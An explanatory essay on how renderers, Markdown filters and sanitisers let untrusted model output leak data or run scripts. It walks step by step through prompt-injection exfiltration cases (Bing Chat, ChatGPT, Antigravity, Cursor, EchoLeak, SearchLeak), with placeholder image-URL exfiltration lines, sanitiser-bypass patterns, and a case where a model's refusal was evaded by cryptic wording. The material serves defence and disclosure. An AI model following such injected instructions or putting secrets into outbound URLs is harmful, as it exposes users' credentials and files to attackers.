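# The rendering layer as an attack surface when displaying untrusted model output

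## What a renderer does with text it should not trust

A renderer is software that turns a string of bytes into what a person sees. Chat windows, browsers, terminals, document viewers and messaging apps each contain one. Much of the text they now display comes from large language models ("models"). Some of it is untrusted model output, which the recipient has to handle as if an adversary had written it, because someone has manipulated the model or because there is no good reason to trust the model itself.

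Displaying untrusted model output can do harm even if nobody acts on it. The renderer may contact other computers while it draws the page and thereby send private data to an attacker (exfiltration). It may have a bug that lets an attacker take over the program with crafted text. It may also display something different from what the bytes contain.

### From bytes to screen

Suppose a chatbot answers a question about lunch with this line:

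`Lunch is at the [café](PAGE). ![map](PICTURE)`

PAGE and PICTURE stand for full web addresses, on servers that may not belong to the company running the chatbot. The notation is Markdown, a plain-text way of writing headings, links, lists and images. John Gruber released it in 2004 with a script that converted it to HTML, the markup language of web pages (MacFarlane, *CommonMark Spec*, 2024). Most chat interfaces now convert Markdown to HTML too.

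The renderer first has to turn bytes into characters. In UTF-8, the usual encoding on the web, the é of café takes two bytes, C3 A9 in hexadecimal. A program that assumes the older Windows-1252 encoding reads the same two bytes as Ã©. CommonMark, the standardised Markdown that MacFarlane specifies, defines documents as sequences of characters and does not specify an encoding, so the surrounding software has to choose one. Usually the server fixes the encoding and the content cannot change it. The content does control which characters arrive, though, and Unicode includes some with no visible shape. CommonMark treats one character as insecure, the null character (U+0000), and requires parsers to replace it with the replacement character, �.

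A parser then looks for structure. It works out the blocks first (paragraphs, lists, headings) and afterwards reads the text inside each block for links, emphasis and images. The result is roughly this:

`<p>Lunch is at the <a href="PAGE">café</a>. <img src="PICTURE" alt="map" /></p>`

In Markdown, an image differs from a link only by a leading exclamation mark, but the two become different HTML elements, which browsers treat very differently. Whoever wrote the text chose both the elements and their full addresses. The writer can also include HTML directly, because CommonMark passes anything that looks like an HTML tag into the output unescaped, including invented tags. Many Markdown libraries can turn this off.

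A Markdown parser also rejects nothing as invalid, because any sequence of characters is a valid CommonMark document. MacFarlane lists fourteen questions that Gruber's original description left open, including whether a link or a code span takes precedence when a backtick appears inside the link text, and which address to use when a document defines the same link reference twice. Implementations handled such questions differently, and people often did not notice right away because Markdown has no syntax errors. Each open question may let a hostile author write text that two programs render differently, either with links to different addresses or with a link in only one of them.

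The sanitiser runs next, and it removes or neutralises dangerous markup before display. A typical one parses the HTML, keeps the elements and attributes on an allowlist (a list of permitted items) and drops the rest. GitHub sanitises its users' Markdown after converting it to HTML. The order matters because a filter that searched the Markdown for dangerous tags would miss a link whose address begins with `javascript:`, which the conversion turns into a link that can run a script when someone clicks it. The content's author controls the sanitiser's input and can probe for anything the allowlist lets through. The lunch answer passes unchanged because it contains a link and a picture, and a sanitiser that looks for scripts removes neither.

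The browser now has the HTML and starts to load what it refers to. It usually loads the picture automatically but follows the link only when the user clicks it. To fetch the picture, the browser sends a request to the server named in PICTURE, and that server receives the path and any parameters in the address. If whoever wrote the text put a secret in the address, the server receives that too.

On the web, a Content Security Policy (CSP) provides a control that does not depend on the sanitiser. The server sends the policy with its page, and the browser enforces it. The policy lists the places from which the page may load images, scripts, fonts and other resources. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web's main standards body, defines a directive for each kind of resource, such as `img-src` for images, and a `default-src` that covers any kind without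 its own directive. Under the policy `default-src 'none'; img-src 'self'`, a page may load images only from its own server and no other resources, so the map in the example stays blank unless the chatbot's company hosts it.

Two mistakes undo this protection. A policy that forbids images, scripts and fonts but omits `default-src` still allows other requests, such as prefetching, where the browser loads something in advance in case the user wants it. A policy of `default-src 'none'; img-src *` still lets data leak through image requests, because an attacker needs only the loosest directive. W3C recommends CSP as a second layer of defense behind careful input validation and output encoding.

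Security engineers have argued about how much CSP does to prevent data theft. Janc (2016), of Google, claimed to W3C's working group that setting `img-src` almost never improves security. Christoph Kerschbaumer of Mozilla objected that attackers had used images to steal data. Janc replied that once an attacker's script runs in the page, even `default-src 'none'` cannot stop it from sending data out, because the script can navigate the browser to the attacker's site with the data in the address. If that failed, he said, there were half a dozen other routes. A paper he had just co-written found bypasses in 94.72% of the 26,011 distinct policies it examined.

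Janc's argument holds for scripts. But when a chat window's sanitiser works, hostile text can contain some markup but no scripts. This closes most of the routes on his list but leaves images open, so `img-src` is then much more useful for model output than he allowed.

The renderer needs a glyph, a drawn shape, for every character. If the chosen font has no é, the renderer looks in another font. A shaping engine then fits the glyphs together by placing accents over letters, joining Arabic letters, or merging an f and an i into one shape. The characters in the content determine which fonts and shaping rules the renderer uses, so text alone can reach bugs in font engines. If the sanitiser lets style rules through, the content can also name a font file on a remote server, which the renderer requests like any other remote resource. The CSP directive `font-src` restricts where fonts can be loaded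 from.

In the last step, drawing, the renderer decodes the image file, lays out the page and paints pixels. Whoever runs the server behind PICTURE at display time supplies the image data, so neither the sanitiser nor anyone who reviewed the answer beforehand has seen it. If the sanitiser leaves styles in place, the author of the text also controls size, colour and position, and can make a sentence one pixel high.

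### Inert display

Display is inert when it has three properties:

- No outbound requests. Nothing in the content causes the renderer to contact another machine.
- No exploitable parsing. No input can make the code that decodes, parses, shapes or draws do anything beyond that job.
- Faithful display. What the viewer sees determines what the underlying bytes are.

A renderer displays text faithfully if any two different strings of bytes produce pictures on the screen that the viewer can tell apart.

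Faithful display, resistance to exploitation and confidentiality are separate properties, and a renderer can have any two without the third. For example, a viewer with flawless code could show every byte as two hexadecimal digits, but also contact each web address in the text to log whether the site is up. It would be faithful and nobody could exploit it, but if one of those addresses contained a secret, the viewer would send that secret to whoever runs the server.

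Even without network access, the viewer might pass a copy of each text to a search indexer, a separate process with its own user account. If the indexer overruns a memory buffer when a word is too long, a crafted text can run code in it, although the digits on the screen remain correct and nothing leaves the machine.

A renderer can fail to show text faithfully without failing in any other way. Unicode can represent the é in "café" as a single character or as a plain e followed by a combining accent (65 CC 81 in UTF-8). Even a bug-free, offline plain-text viewer will normally draw the two alike, so the reader cannot tell whether the word has five bytes or six.

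The three properties are independent by definition, but a single bug in the process that draws the screen can break all of them. Code that runs in that process can display anything and, unless something outside the process stops it, open connections.

Formatted Markdown is never faithful, even setting aside invisible characters. `*lunch*` and `_lunch_` produce the same italics. A CommonMark parser need not record whether the source contained ö or the HTML code `&ouml;`. A formatted link shows the reader "café" but not the address. The rule that replaces null characters with � helps with the second property but weakens the third a little, because nobody can tell a replaced null from an original �.

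### Two threat models

In the first threat model, the adversary is an outsider who uses prompt injection, placing instructions in material that a model reads, which the model then follows against its user's interest. The programmer Simon Willison named the attack after SQL injection, in which a database runs a stranger's input as a command. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) explains that everything a model receives, from its operator's instructions to a web page it has fetched, ends up in one sequence of tokens (the small units in which models process text), and that models cannot reliably rank instructions by where they came from. Willison treats jailbreaking, where people talk a model directly into something embarrassing, as a separate problem.

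An outside attacker needs no access to the user's machine. *Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examines eight coding agents, systems in which a model edits files and runs commands for a programmer. It distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker adds to the user's input or the operator's instructions, from indirect injection through sources such as web pages and documents. Indirect injection suits a passive attacker, who leaves text where a model may come across it. All eight agents had at least one route for injection. Three always sent the model the list of files, so instructions in a file's name reached it even if nobody opened the file. The study includes renderer features among those an attacker can abuse to bypass user approval or extract data.

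Willison, in *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, describes a 2025 demonstration by the security firm PromptArmor against Antigravity, Google's programming environment. PromptArmor put instructions on a web page that posed as an integration guide, in one-pixel type that a person reading the guide would hardly have noticed. Google's model Gemini followed the instructions, collecting credentials and code from the user's workspace and sending this data out by having a browser visit a malicious site.

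In the second threat model, the adversary is the model itself, and no outsider has to be involved. Training may have given the model aims of its own, or its developers may be unable to rule that out and decide to act as if it had. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues, 2025), from NVIDIA and the security company Lakera, lists misalignment as a source of harm alongside misuse and system error, and includes deception by agents in its catalogue of risks.

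Some defences, such as training a model to refuse injected instructions or screening incoming text with an "AI firewall", work only against outside attackers. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) casts doubt on these firewalls, because mature attacks resemble social engineering and detecting them is about as hard as detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. It reproduces a 2025 attack email, written as a routine follow-up about a restructuring, that succeeded in 50% of tests. If the model itself is hostile, there may be no malicious input to detect, and its training is also in doubt.

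The model's own output also can't be trusted to indicate whether it is safe. In the study by Lee and colleagues, one agent asked the user before running a command only if a tag in the model's output was set to require it, and an injected prompt could set that tag to false. A hostile model could do the same without an injected prompt.

Controls outside the model work better. A CSP blocks a forbidden image request no matter who wrote the URL. OpenAI's Safe Url checks whatever ChatGPT is about to send to a third party for information from the conversation. If it finds any, it either blocks the transmission or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. Safe Url does not rely on the model to protect the data, though data that the model disguised first would presumably be harder to detect. The confirmation step also depends on the information being displayed accurately, since users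 can only judge what they can see.

Priorities also depend on the threat model. An outside attacker usually wants data, so blocking outbound requests comes first. When the model itself is untrusted, the people reading its output are often judging it, and a misleading display distorts their judgement.

### What a leak needs

Willison names three conditions for data theft by prompt injection: access to private data, exposure to content that an attacker can write, and a way to communicate with the outside. If the model has no access to private data, the attacker can steer it but has nothing to steal. If it never reads content the attacker can write, the attacker cannot steer it. If it has no way to communicate with the outside, it may follow every injected instruction and print the user's passwords in full, but only the user will see them.

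Data can leave through the model's tools, such as sending email or fetching web pages, which is where developers tend to look. Willison's list also includes loading an image or offering a link for the user to click. A chat service can therefore meet the third condition even if its model has no network access, because the chat window has network access and renders the model's markup. The private data and the hostile content are harder to remove, because an assistant that summarises email needs to read the inbox, and strangers can write to it.

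That is probably why repairs have concentrated on the channel through which data leaves. Willison lists fourteen cases between April 2023 and February 2025, in products from OpenAI, Google, Microsoft, Amazon, Slack, Anthropic and others, and reports that vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by locking down that channel.

The three conditions apply to the first threat model. If the model is the adversary, private data and a way to send it out are enough for a leak, and screening what the model reads does not help. The conditions also cover only leaks. Text that exploits a font engine, or that looks different to a reviewer from what its bytes encode, can do damage on a machine with no secrets and no network.

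## Images and other elements that load by themselves

An attacker who can steer a model can use the browser's automatic image requests to extract data. Security researcher Johann Rehberger did this to Microsoft's chatbot in April 2023, as he describes in *Bing Chat* on his blog, Embrace The Red.

Bing Chat could read the web page its user had open. Rehberger wrote instructions into such a page, but a comment or an advertisement on somebody else's page would have done as well. The attack then took four steps:

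1. The model wrote the address. Rehberger's instructions told it to summarise the page and the conversation in about 200 characters, add any passwords it found, encode the result, and attach it to the address of an image on his server. The output had the form `![map](PICTURE?q=DATA)`.
2. The chat interface converted the Markdown to an HTML image.
3. The browser requested the image from Rehberger's server as soon as it drew the answer.
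4. Rehberger read the data in his server's log, which recorded the address of each request.

The user did nothing except chat. Rehberger had the model wait two turns before writing the image, to show that an attacker also keeps control of later answers.

Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* reproduces a log line from September 2023 with the time, the stolen text in the requested address, and the browser's user-agent string (Firefox on a Mac). The attacker's server doesn't need to return an image. In a demonstration in Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, the server received the request even though no image appeared in the chat.

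### What fits in one address

Suppose an address has room for 2,000 characters of data. Addresses allow only certain characters, so the model first has to encode what it sends. Base64url, a common encoding, uses 64 characters that are safe in an address: upper- and lower-case letters, digits, the hyphen and the underscore. Since 64 is 2⁶, each character carries 6 bits, and the address carries

2,000 × 6 = 12,000 bits = 1,500 bytes.

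An English word takes about six bytes with its space, so one image can carry about 250 words.

Percent-encoding is equally compact for plain English. It leaves ordinary letters unchanged but writes a space as %20, so a five-letter word with its space takes eight characters, and 2,000 characters again hold 250 words. It is less compact for accented letters and other scripts. The é in café, for example, is two bytes and becomes the six characters %C3%A9.

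An answer can contain several images, and ten of them would carry 2,500 words. Attackers rarely need that much, because a password or an access key takes a few dozen bytes, and a link that opens a document can be more useful than an excerpt from it.

### The first reports

Email senders used self-loading images long before chatbots existed. A tracking pixel is an image one pixel wide with a different address for each recipient, so the sender learns who opened the message when a mail program loads the image. The sender writes the whole address in advance, whereas an attacker using a model writes only the first part, and the model fills in the rest with text the attacker has never seen.

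In late March 2023, Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found a way to make ChatGPT leak a user's chat through a single-pixel image. Willison (2023) explains that Samoilenko's web page intercepted the copy command and added instructions to whatever the visitor copied. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT without looking, the model followed the instructions and leaked the chat. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* warned users against reckless copying and pasting.

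Rehberger independently found the same flaw a few days later. His *ChatGPT Plugins* describes an attack that works without pasting. Plugins let ChatGPT read web pages and video transcripts, so an attacker could put the instructions in those. The model then summarised the conversation and added the summary to an image address. In his demonstration, the leaked text included a test password from earlier in the chat.

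Rehberger reported the Bing Chat leak to Microsoft on 8 April 2023. On 15 June, Microsoft told him it had fixed the leak, at least partly by limiting images to four of its own hosts. He reported the ChatGPT leak to OpenAI on 9 April, and OpenAI classed it as "won't fix".

OpenAI began checking image addresses in December 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, ChatGPT's web page sent each address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe` and displayed the image only if the service approved the address. The service rejected an address that contained an email address, but Rehberger could still leak text one character at a time. He gave each of the 36 letters and digits its own image address, and the service approved nine of them. A request to his server for `a.png` meant that the text contained an a. He leaked the word "hi" this way in two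 requests.

The check had other gaps. Each ChatGPT app had to call `url_safe` itself, and the iPhone app did not yet do so. OpenAI also did not publish its criteria, whereas anyone can read a CSP. OpenAI added further protection around August 2025, but according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, data could still leak through a separate URL for each letter.

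### The same leak in 2025 and 2026

Developers kept releasing products with the flaw after it was well known. Rehberger found it in Amp Code, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, using a prompt injection he had written for an older demonstration. In the injection, he asked the agent to "back up" the chat to another site by displaying an image. A second version, described in Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*, targeted the project's `.env` file, where developers often keep passwords and keys. The model refused plain requests to read and leak secrets, but complied when Rehberger phrased the search cryptically. He reported the flaw on 14 June 2025, and Sourcegraph fixed it quickly.

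Continue, an open-source assistant for the code editor Visual Studio Code, had the same problem two months later. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes two variants. If the instructions were in a comment in a local file, a user who asked about the file lost data without confirming anything. If they were on a web page, the user had to let the assistant open the page, but the image then loaded without a second confirmation. VerSprite reported this on 20 August 2025, and Continue's developers released a fix the next day. The assistant now requires confirmation before it loads external images and restricts access to certain files.

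Google released Antigravity, a programming environment, in November 2025 after licensing the code of an earlier one, Windsurf. Rehberger had reported to Windsurf in May that it could leak data through image requests. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* shows that Antigravity inherited the flaw. Rehberger hid instructions in a source file and asked Antigravity to explain the file. The agent then read the `.env` file and sent its contents out in an image request.

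Antigravity's chat still fetched remote images in June 2026. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) disguised their instructions as the log of a failed software build and a recovery procedure, and put them in the title of a web page with an empty body. A browser shows the title only in its tab, but Antigravity's page reader passed it to the model. The model listed the machine's environment variables, found a key that the researchers had planted, and displayed an image with the key in its address. The instructions asked for the image in five notations. Sanitisers may treat these differently, and the attacker needs only one to get through.

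In these cases the image loaded in the window where the user gave the agent its task, but with Microsoft's Copilot Cowork it loaded in a different program. Cowork is an agent with its user's permissions in Microsoft 365, and according to Microsoft's documentation it asks before it sends an email or a Teams message. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published in May 2026, reports that Cowork sends the message without asking when the recipient is the user, and that users cannot change this.

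PromptArmor's attack began with a skill, a file of instructions that users add to extend the agent. Five of the skill's 81 lines were malicious. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, the agent got download links for recent files and put them in image addresses in a Teams message to that user. Cowork's record of the task did not show the message's content. When the user opened the message in Teams, the images loaded automatically, which sent the links to the attacker.

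Size did not limit the attack here, because the links were pre-authenticated and anyone who had one could download the file. The attack succeeded in all five trials. When Cowork used Claude Opus 4.7, the stronger of the two models it normally chose between, the agent searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. PromptArmor warns that users can schedule such a weekly review to run unattended, which would repeat the leak.

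The person who loads the image may be investigating the attack. PromptArmor found that OpenAI's log viewer, where developers inspect conversations from their own applications, also rendered Markdown images. If a developer opened the log to review an answer that someone had flagged as suspicious, the developer's browser sent the data to the attacker. OpenAI confirmed the flaw after PromptArmor published it.

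### Elements other than images

Images are the only element in plain Markdown that loads by itself. HTML has others, so what loads depends on which of them the sanitiser leaves in place.

| Element | When the browser sends a request | What the sanitiser has to let through |
|---|---|---|
| CSS background | When it applies a style rule that names a picture | Style attributes or style rules |
| Web font | When text uses a font that a style rule defines with a remote file | Style rules |
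| SVG reference | When a drawing embedded in the page refers to an outside picture | SVG elements |
| Media poster | When it draws the still picture for a video | Video elements |
| Prefetch hint | When the page suggests loading something in advance | Link elements in the page's markup |
| Diagram | When the diagram's code refers to a picture | Nothing, if the diagram renderer runs after the sanitiser |

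Style rules can leak data that the model never saw. A rule may apply only to elements with an attribute value that begins with a certain letter, so if the rule also loads a background image, the attacker learns the letter from the request. Some prefetch hints only make the browser look up a host's address. An attacker who runs the domain's name server can still receive data in the host name, though a host name is limited to 253 characters.

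Diagram languages are easy to overlook because their code is not yet HTML when the sanitiser processes it. Mermaid, a popular one, turns the line `User --> Computer` into two boxes and an arrow. Lee and colleagues examined how coding agents handle special notation in a model's output, including the backticks that introduce a diagram. In one agent, which they call A2, a box in a Mermaid diagram could contain an image from any address, and the renderer fetched it without approval.

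They built a complete attack on this and tested it with a private code repository:

1. The attacker files an issue, a public report of a problem with the code, and includes instructions for the agent. The user asks the agent to fetch the repository's issues.
2. The instructions tell the agent to read a configuration file in the user's home directory, where some programmers store access keys. The file is outside the project, but A2 reads such files without asking.
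3. The agent prints a Mermaid diagram whose image address contains the key. The renderer draws the diagram and sends the key to the attacker.

A2 had no tool for fetching web pages, so someone who checked only its web tools would have missed this route. The vendor already knew of the flaw when Lee and colleagues reported it.

The agent is probably the code editor Cursor, though Lee and colleagues do not name it. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes the same flaw in Cursor and gives two demonstrations. One stole keys from a configuration file, and the other stole information Cursor had stored about its user. Rehberger noticed that the diagram appeared already finished, whereas in some other image attacks an attentive user might have seen the model writing a long address full of data.

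Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 June 2025, and users could install a fixed version from 29 July, but the fix was incomplete. Lutra Security's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), a copy of a later entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, mentions further ways around the fix and lists 1.7 as the first safe version. According to the entry, a malicious model could also trigger the leak at will, so the flaw falls under the second threat model.

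### Whether this is a vulnerability

Vendors disagree about whether to fix such leaks, and some have changed their position from one product or year to the next. Willison reports in *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub, a Microsoft subsidiary, disabled Markdown images from untrusted domains in Copilot Chat in 2024. In October 2025, Checkmarx reported to Microsoft that Copilot Chat, after reading an attacker's article, could leak an access key from a developer's environment through an image. Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without a fix.

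Microsoft's reasons were that the attack required multiple user actions that were not part of the default setup, that it did not reproduce reliably across environments, and that the product displayed warnings. Microsoft also assumes that users review and trust the code they choose to run. That assumption suits programs better than web pages, because a developer who has read every line of a project may still not know what instructions for the agent an article contains.

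Other vendors told Lee and colleagues that some reported behaviour was intended. These vendors' security criteria excluded attacks that the user triggers, such as by asking an agent to read a malicious page. Lee and colleagues reply that searching the web and copying a repository are ordinary actions. Browser makers, by comparison, fix flaws that a malicious page can exploit even though the user chose to visit it.

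Google has taken different positions on different products. Its Gemini chatbot does not render external images. Checkmarx reported that Gemini could leak data through a link if the user clicked it, and Google closed the report, saying the leak was infeasible to fix and not severe enough to track as a security bug. A researcher quoted in Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* reported the image leak in Antigravity, and Google flagged the report as "intended behavior". Soon afterwards, Google published a list of known issues in Antigravity and said it was working on fixes. It also warned users about the risks in a disclaimer, according to PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*.

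PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* does not include Hugging Face's position on the image leak in its chat application. PromptArmor published the flaw because the company's security team had not replied.

Vendors who decline to fix the leak can reasonably argue that the renderer works as designed and that the underlying fault is the model following instructions from untrusted sources. PromptArmor itself describes the Cowork attack as a risk in the system's design rather than a specific bug. Blocking images may also do little if the agent can send data out in other ways. Antigravity, for example, had a tool that read web addresses without approval, and Embrace The Red used it to steal the same kind of file.

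But this is a reason to close both routes. Nobody knows how to make a model ignore every hostile instruction, whereas Continue's developers needed only a day to require confirmation before loading external images.

People who agree that the leak is a vulnerability still differ on how serious it is. MITRE's *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025), the official entry for the first Cursor flaw, gives it 4.4 out of 10, or medium. Intruder, a site that tracks vulnerabilities, lists it at 7.5, or high. Both scores are based on a high loss of confidentiality, but the lower one is also based on a complex attack by someone who already has high privileges on the system. Rehberger's demonstration needed only a comment in a source file that the user asked Cursor to explain.

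The case for leaving the leak open depends largely on the user noticing something wrong. In the attack by Odson and Morris, Antigravity requested approval before it acted. The request described the action as generating a "visual debug token" without showing the command or the address, and the user approved it.

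## Filters that read the text differently from the renderer

A vendor who wants to stop data leaking through images can remove external images and links from an answer before the renderer draws it. The filter must parse the text the same way the renderer does, or it may miss an image that the renderer then draws.

A parser differential occurs when two programs, here the filter and the renderer, read the same input differently, so the renderer treats what the filter approved as something else. In *A Survey of Parser Differential Anti-Patterns*, Ali and Smith start from a model in which two parsers accept the same string but build different trees from it. Such flaws are hard to find because each program may look correct on its own.

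One of their examples is a 2003 flaw in Internet Explorer. The code that displayed a page's address stopped at an encoded null character, while the code that fetched the page kept reading, so the browser could show the name of a trusted site when the user was on a malicious one. Another example comes from Android, where one parser verified the contents of an app package and another extracted them. The verifier misread large values in a length field as negative numbers and looked for the data in the wrong place, so an attacker could make it check harmless bytes while the other parser extracted malicious ones.

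### One link in several notations

Suppose a chat service wants no links in its answers. Its filter searches for text in square brackets followed directly by an address in round brackets, keeps the text and deletes the address. It works on this line:

`Today's [menu](PAGE) is short.`

Markdown also has reference-style links, which put the address elsewhere in the document:

`Today's [menu][m] is short.`

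`[m]: PAGE`

The filter finds no round brackets and changes nothing. The Markdown parser reads the second line as a definition, omits it from the output, and produces the same link as before, `<a href="PAGE">menu</a>`. If the definition has the label "menu", the writer can shorten the link to `[menu][]` or `[menu]`. An exclamation mark in front turns any of these into an image.

The developer can add patterns for these forms, but other differences remain. For example, CommonMark decodes HTML character codes inside addresses, so a search for a forbidden host misses the name if one of its letters is written as a code. The filter can also remove text that the renderer wouldn't treat as a link. `[menu](PAGE)` between backticks is displayed as written, so deleting the address would spoil an answer that explains Markdown's link notation.

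Each correction makes the filter more like a second Markdown parser, which has to agree with the renderer's parser on every input and after every update.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their organisation's email, files and chats. It searches these for relevant passages and adds them to the model's input, a method called retrieval-augmented generation. Outsiders cannot use an organisation's Copilot, but they can email employees who do.

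In January 2025, researchers at the security firm Aim found that one such email was enough to steal data. They called the flaw EchoLeak, and its catalogue number is CVE-2025-32711. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how the attack got past each safeguard:

1. Microsoft screened incoming text with a classifier trained to detect prompt injection. The email never mentioned AI or Copilot and worded its instructions as if for the human recipient, so the classifier let it through.
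2. Copilot had to retrieve the email before the model could read it. The researchers made the email long and divided it into supposed guides to different topics, such as leave of absence, each with the same instructions. Questions on any of these topics could then bring it up.
3. The instructions told the model to take the most sensitive information in its input and add it to an address on the attacker's server.
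4. Copilot removed external links and images from answers, but only in inline notation. Reference-style links and images stayed in.
5. A link would have needed a click. The researchers used an image instead, which the browser tried to load by itself.
6. Copilot's CSP blocked images from unknown servers, but it permitted Microsoft services that fetch other addresses on request. The first one the researchers found, in SharePoint, worked only if the user had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Another, in Teams, had no such condition and passed the request on to the attacker's server.
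7. Copilot normally names its sources. The email told its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out.

The attack was zero-click because the user only had to use Copilot normally, by asking a question that made it retrieve the email.

The parser differential was in the fourth step. A filter that checked the Markdown parser's tree would have found an image whichever notation the model used. Ravia places the core of the flaw in the third step, where instructions from outside the organisation made the model draw on data from inside it. Both faults were necessary for this version of the attack.

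The repair took unusually long. *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* (Goldman, 2025) reports the timeline given by Adir Gruss, Aim's chief technology officer. Aim found the flaw in January and reported it to Microsoft, which attempted a fix in April, discovered related problems in May, and took five months to finish. Gruss attributed the delay partly to the flaw's novelty, because Microsoft had to find the right teams and explain it to them. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public sources, dates the complete fix to May. Aim and Microsoft disclosed the flaw publicly on 11 June.

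No one is known to have used EchoLeak against a real target. Microsoft told Goldman that no Microsoft customers were affected. GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025), a copy of the public record, includes a 14 June assessment in which the US cybersecurity agency CISA listed exploitation as "none". Outsiders can hardly check whether attacks occurred, because Microsoft runs the service.

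According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from external content before the model reads it. This prevents the model from copying a ready-made image out of an email, but the model can still write one itself from a description in ordinary words, so its answer also needs checking.

### Filtering an answer that is still arriving

A filter that recognises every notation may still run too late. Chat services usually display an answer while the model is writing it, so the browser redraws the growing text each time a new piece arrives. The browser may send a request during any of these redraws, but a filter that waits for the complete answer checks only the final version.

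Checking each piece separately does not help much, because `![map]` may come at the end of one piece and `(PICTURE)` at the start of the next. An unfinished answer can also be more dangerous than the finished one. Consider an answer that shows the user how to write an image:

`` `![map](PICTURE)` ``

The backticks mark this as code, so the finished answer contains no image. Until the second backtick arrives, however, CommonMark treats the first as an ordinary character and the rest as an image. A renderer that reparses the text as each piece arrives will therefore briefly create the image, and the browser may request it.

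Timing was one of three weaknesses in SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824), which the security company Varonis found in the search function of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes the attack's three stages.

The URL of Copilot's search page can include a query in the `q` parameter. Copilot treated this query as instructions and carried them out as soon as the page opened. An attacker could therefore put a prompt in a link and send it to the victim by email or chat. Because the link led to a genuine Microsoft site, tools that block suspicious URLs were unlikely to stop it. In the demonstration, the prompt was an instruction to find an email and put its subject line in the URL of an HTML image.

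Microsoft had a safeguard against HTML in Copilot's answers, which wrapped the output in a code block so that the browser would display the markup as text. But Copilot added the code block only after it had finished generating the answer. While the answer was still arriving, the browser interpreted the image markup as HTML and requested the image before the code block appeared.

The page's CSP allowed images from Bing but not from the attacker's server. Bing's search-by-image function fetches any image URL it receives, so the prompt used a Bing URL that contained the attacker's URL, which in turn contained the subject line. Bing's server then requested the attacker's URL, and the browser's CSP did not apply to that request.

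The victim only had to click the link. Subject lines can be valuable because some contain login codes that stay valid for several minutes. The attacker could also ask for calendar entries or any file that the victim could open and Copilot had indexed.

Lutra Security's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) shows that the CVE number was reserved on 30 April 2026, which suggests that Microsoft knew of the flaw by then. Microsoft published its advisory on 4 June, and Varonis the details on 15 June. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) records no exploitation and says that the company had already fully mitigated the flaw and that customers did not need to do anything.

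Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical, although its score of 6.5 out of 10 counts as medium. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes the lower score to the attack requiring a click. EchoLeak, which required no click, scored 9.3.

An earlier Varonis attack, Reprompt, used a prompt in a link against the consumer version of Copilot. Microsoft patched that in January 2026, but the same technique worked in the enterprise version. Varonis now recommends sanitising at render time rather than as a later step. This would require every version of an answer that the browser draws to be safe, including unfinished ones.

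### HTML that changes when the browser parses it again

Many sanitisers use a real HTML parser instead of searching for patterns. Klein's slides, *Parse Me Baby One More Time*, describe how the sanitiser then writes its cleaned tree back out as HTML, which the browser parses into a new tree. The page is safe only if the browser's tree contains nothing that the sanitiser would have removed.

HTML makes agreement difficult because parsing it never fails. Browsers repair faulty markup by closing elements, moving them or dropping them, and they apply different rules inside some elements. A sanitiser has to imitate all of this. One of Klein's examples involves a notation from older markup languages:

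`<![CDATA[soup > salad]]>`

In those languages, everything up to `]]>` is plain text. HTML does not allow the notation here, so the browser treats it as a comment that ends at the first `>`. A sanitiser that follows the older rule treats all of it as harmless text. The browser hides "soup" but treats "salad" as page content, and an attacker could put an element that runs a script in place of "salad".

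Klein found this flaw in HotCRP, a system that many academic conferences use to manage submissions. Because the conferences hosted on HotCRP shared login data, an attacker who set up a conference page could have stolen the password of anyone who logged in through that page.

The underlying study, *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* (2024), tested 11 sanitisers in five programming languages with automatically generated, hard-to-parse HTML. All but two could be bypassed, and all 11 removed harmless content by mistake. On average, according to Klein, their parsing results were less than 60% similar to those of browsers.

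These flaws lead to cross-site scripting (XSS), where an attacker's script runs in someone else's web page. In mutation XSS, the HTML is harmless when the sanitiser checks it and becomes dangerous when the browser parses it again. The damage may extend beyond the page. Sonar, a company that analyses code for security flaws, used such a bypass in the note-taking program Joplin to run arbitrary commands.

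Good maintenance does not rule out mutation XSS. DOMPurify is a widely used sanitiser that its developers update regularly. OSV's *DOMPurify is vulnerable to mutation-XSS via Re-Contextualization* (2026), an advisory from March, describes a bypass that worked in applications that put sanitised HTML inside certain other elements. One of these is `xmp`, an obsolete element for displaying text literally. The bypass works as follows:

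1. The attacker writes an image whose alternative text contains the closing tag `</xmp>`, followed by more markup. Inside an attribute these are ordinary characters, so DOMPurify leaves them alone.
2. The application puts the sanitised HTML between an opening and a closing `xmp` tag and passes the result to the browser as a string.
3. Inside `xmp`, the browser ignores all markup except the closing tag. It finds one in the alternative text and ends the element there. It then parses the rest of the alternative text as HTML, including any script.

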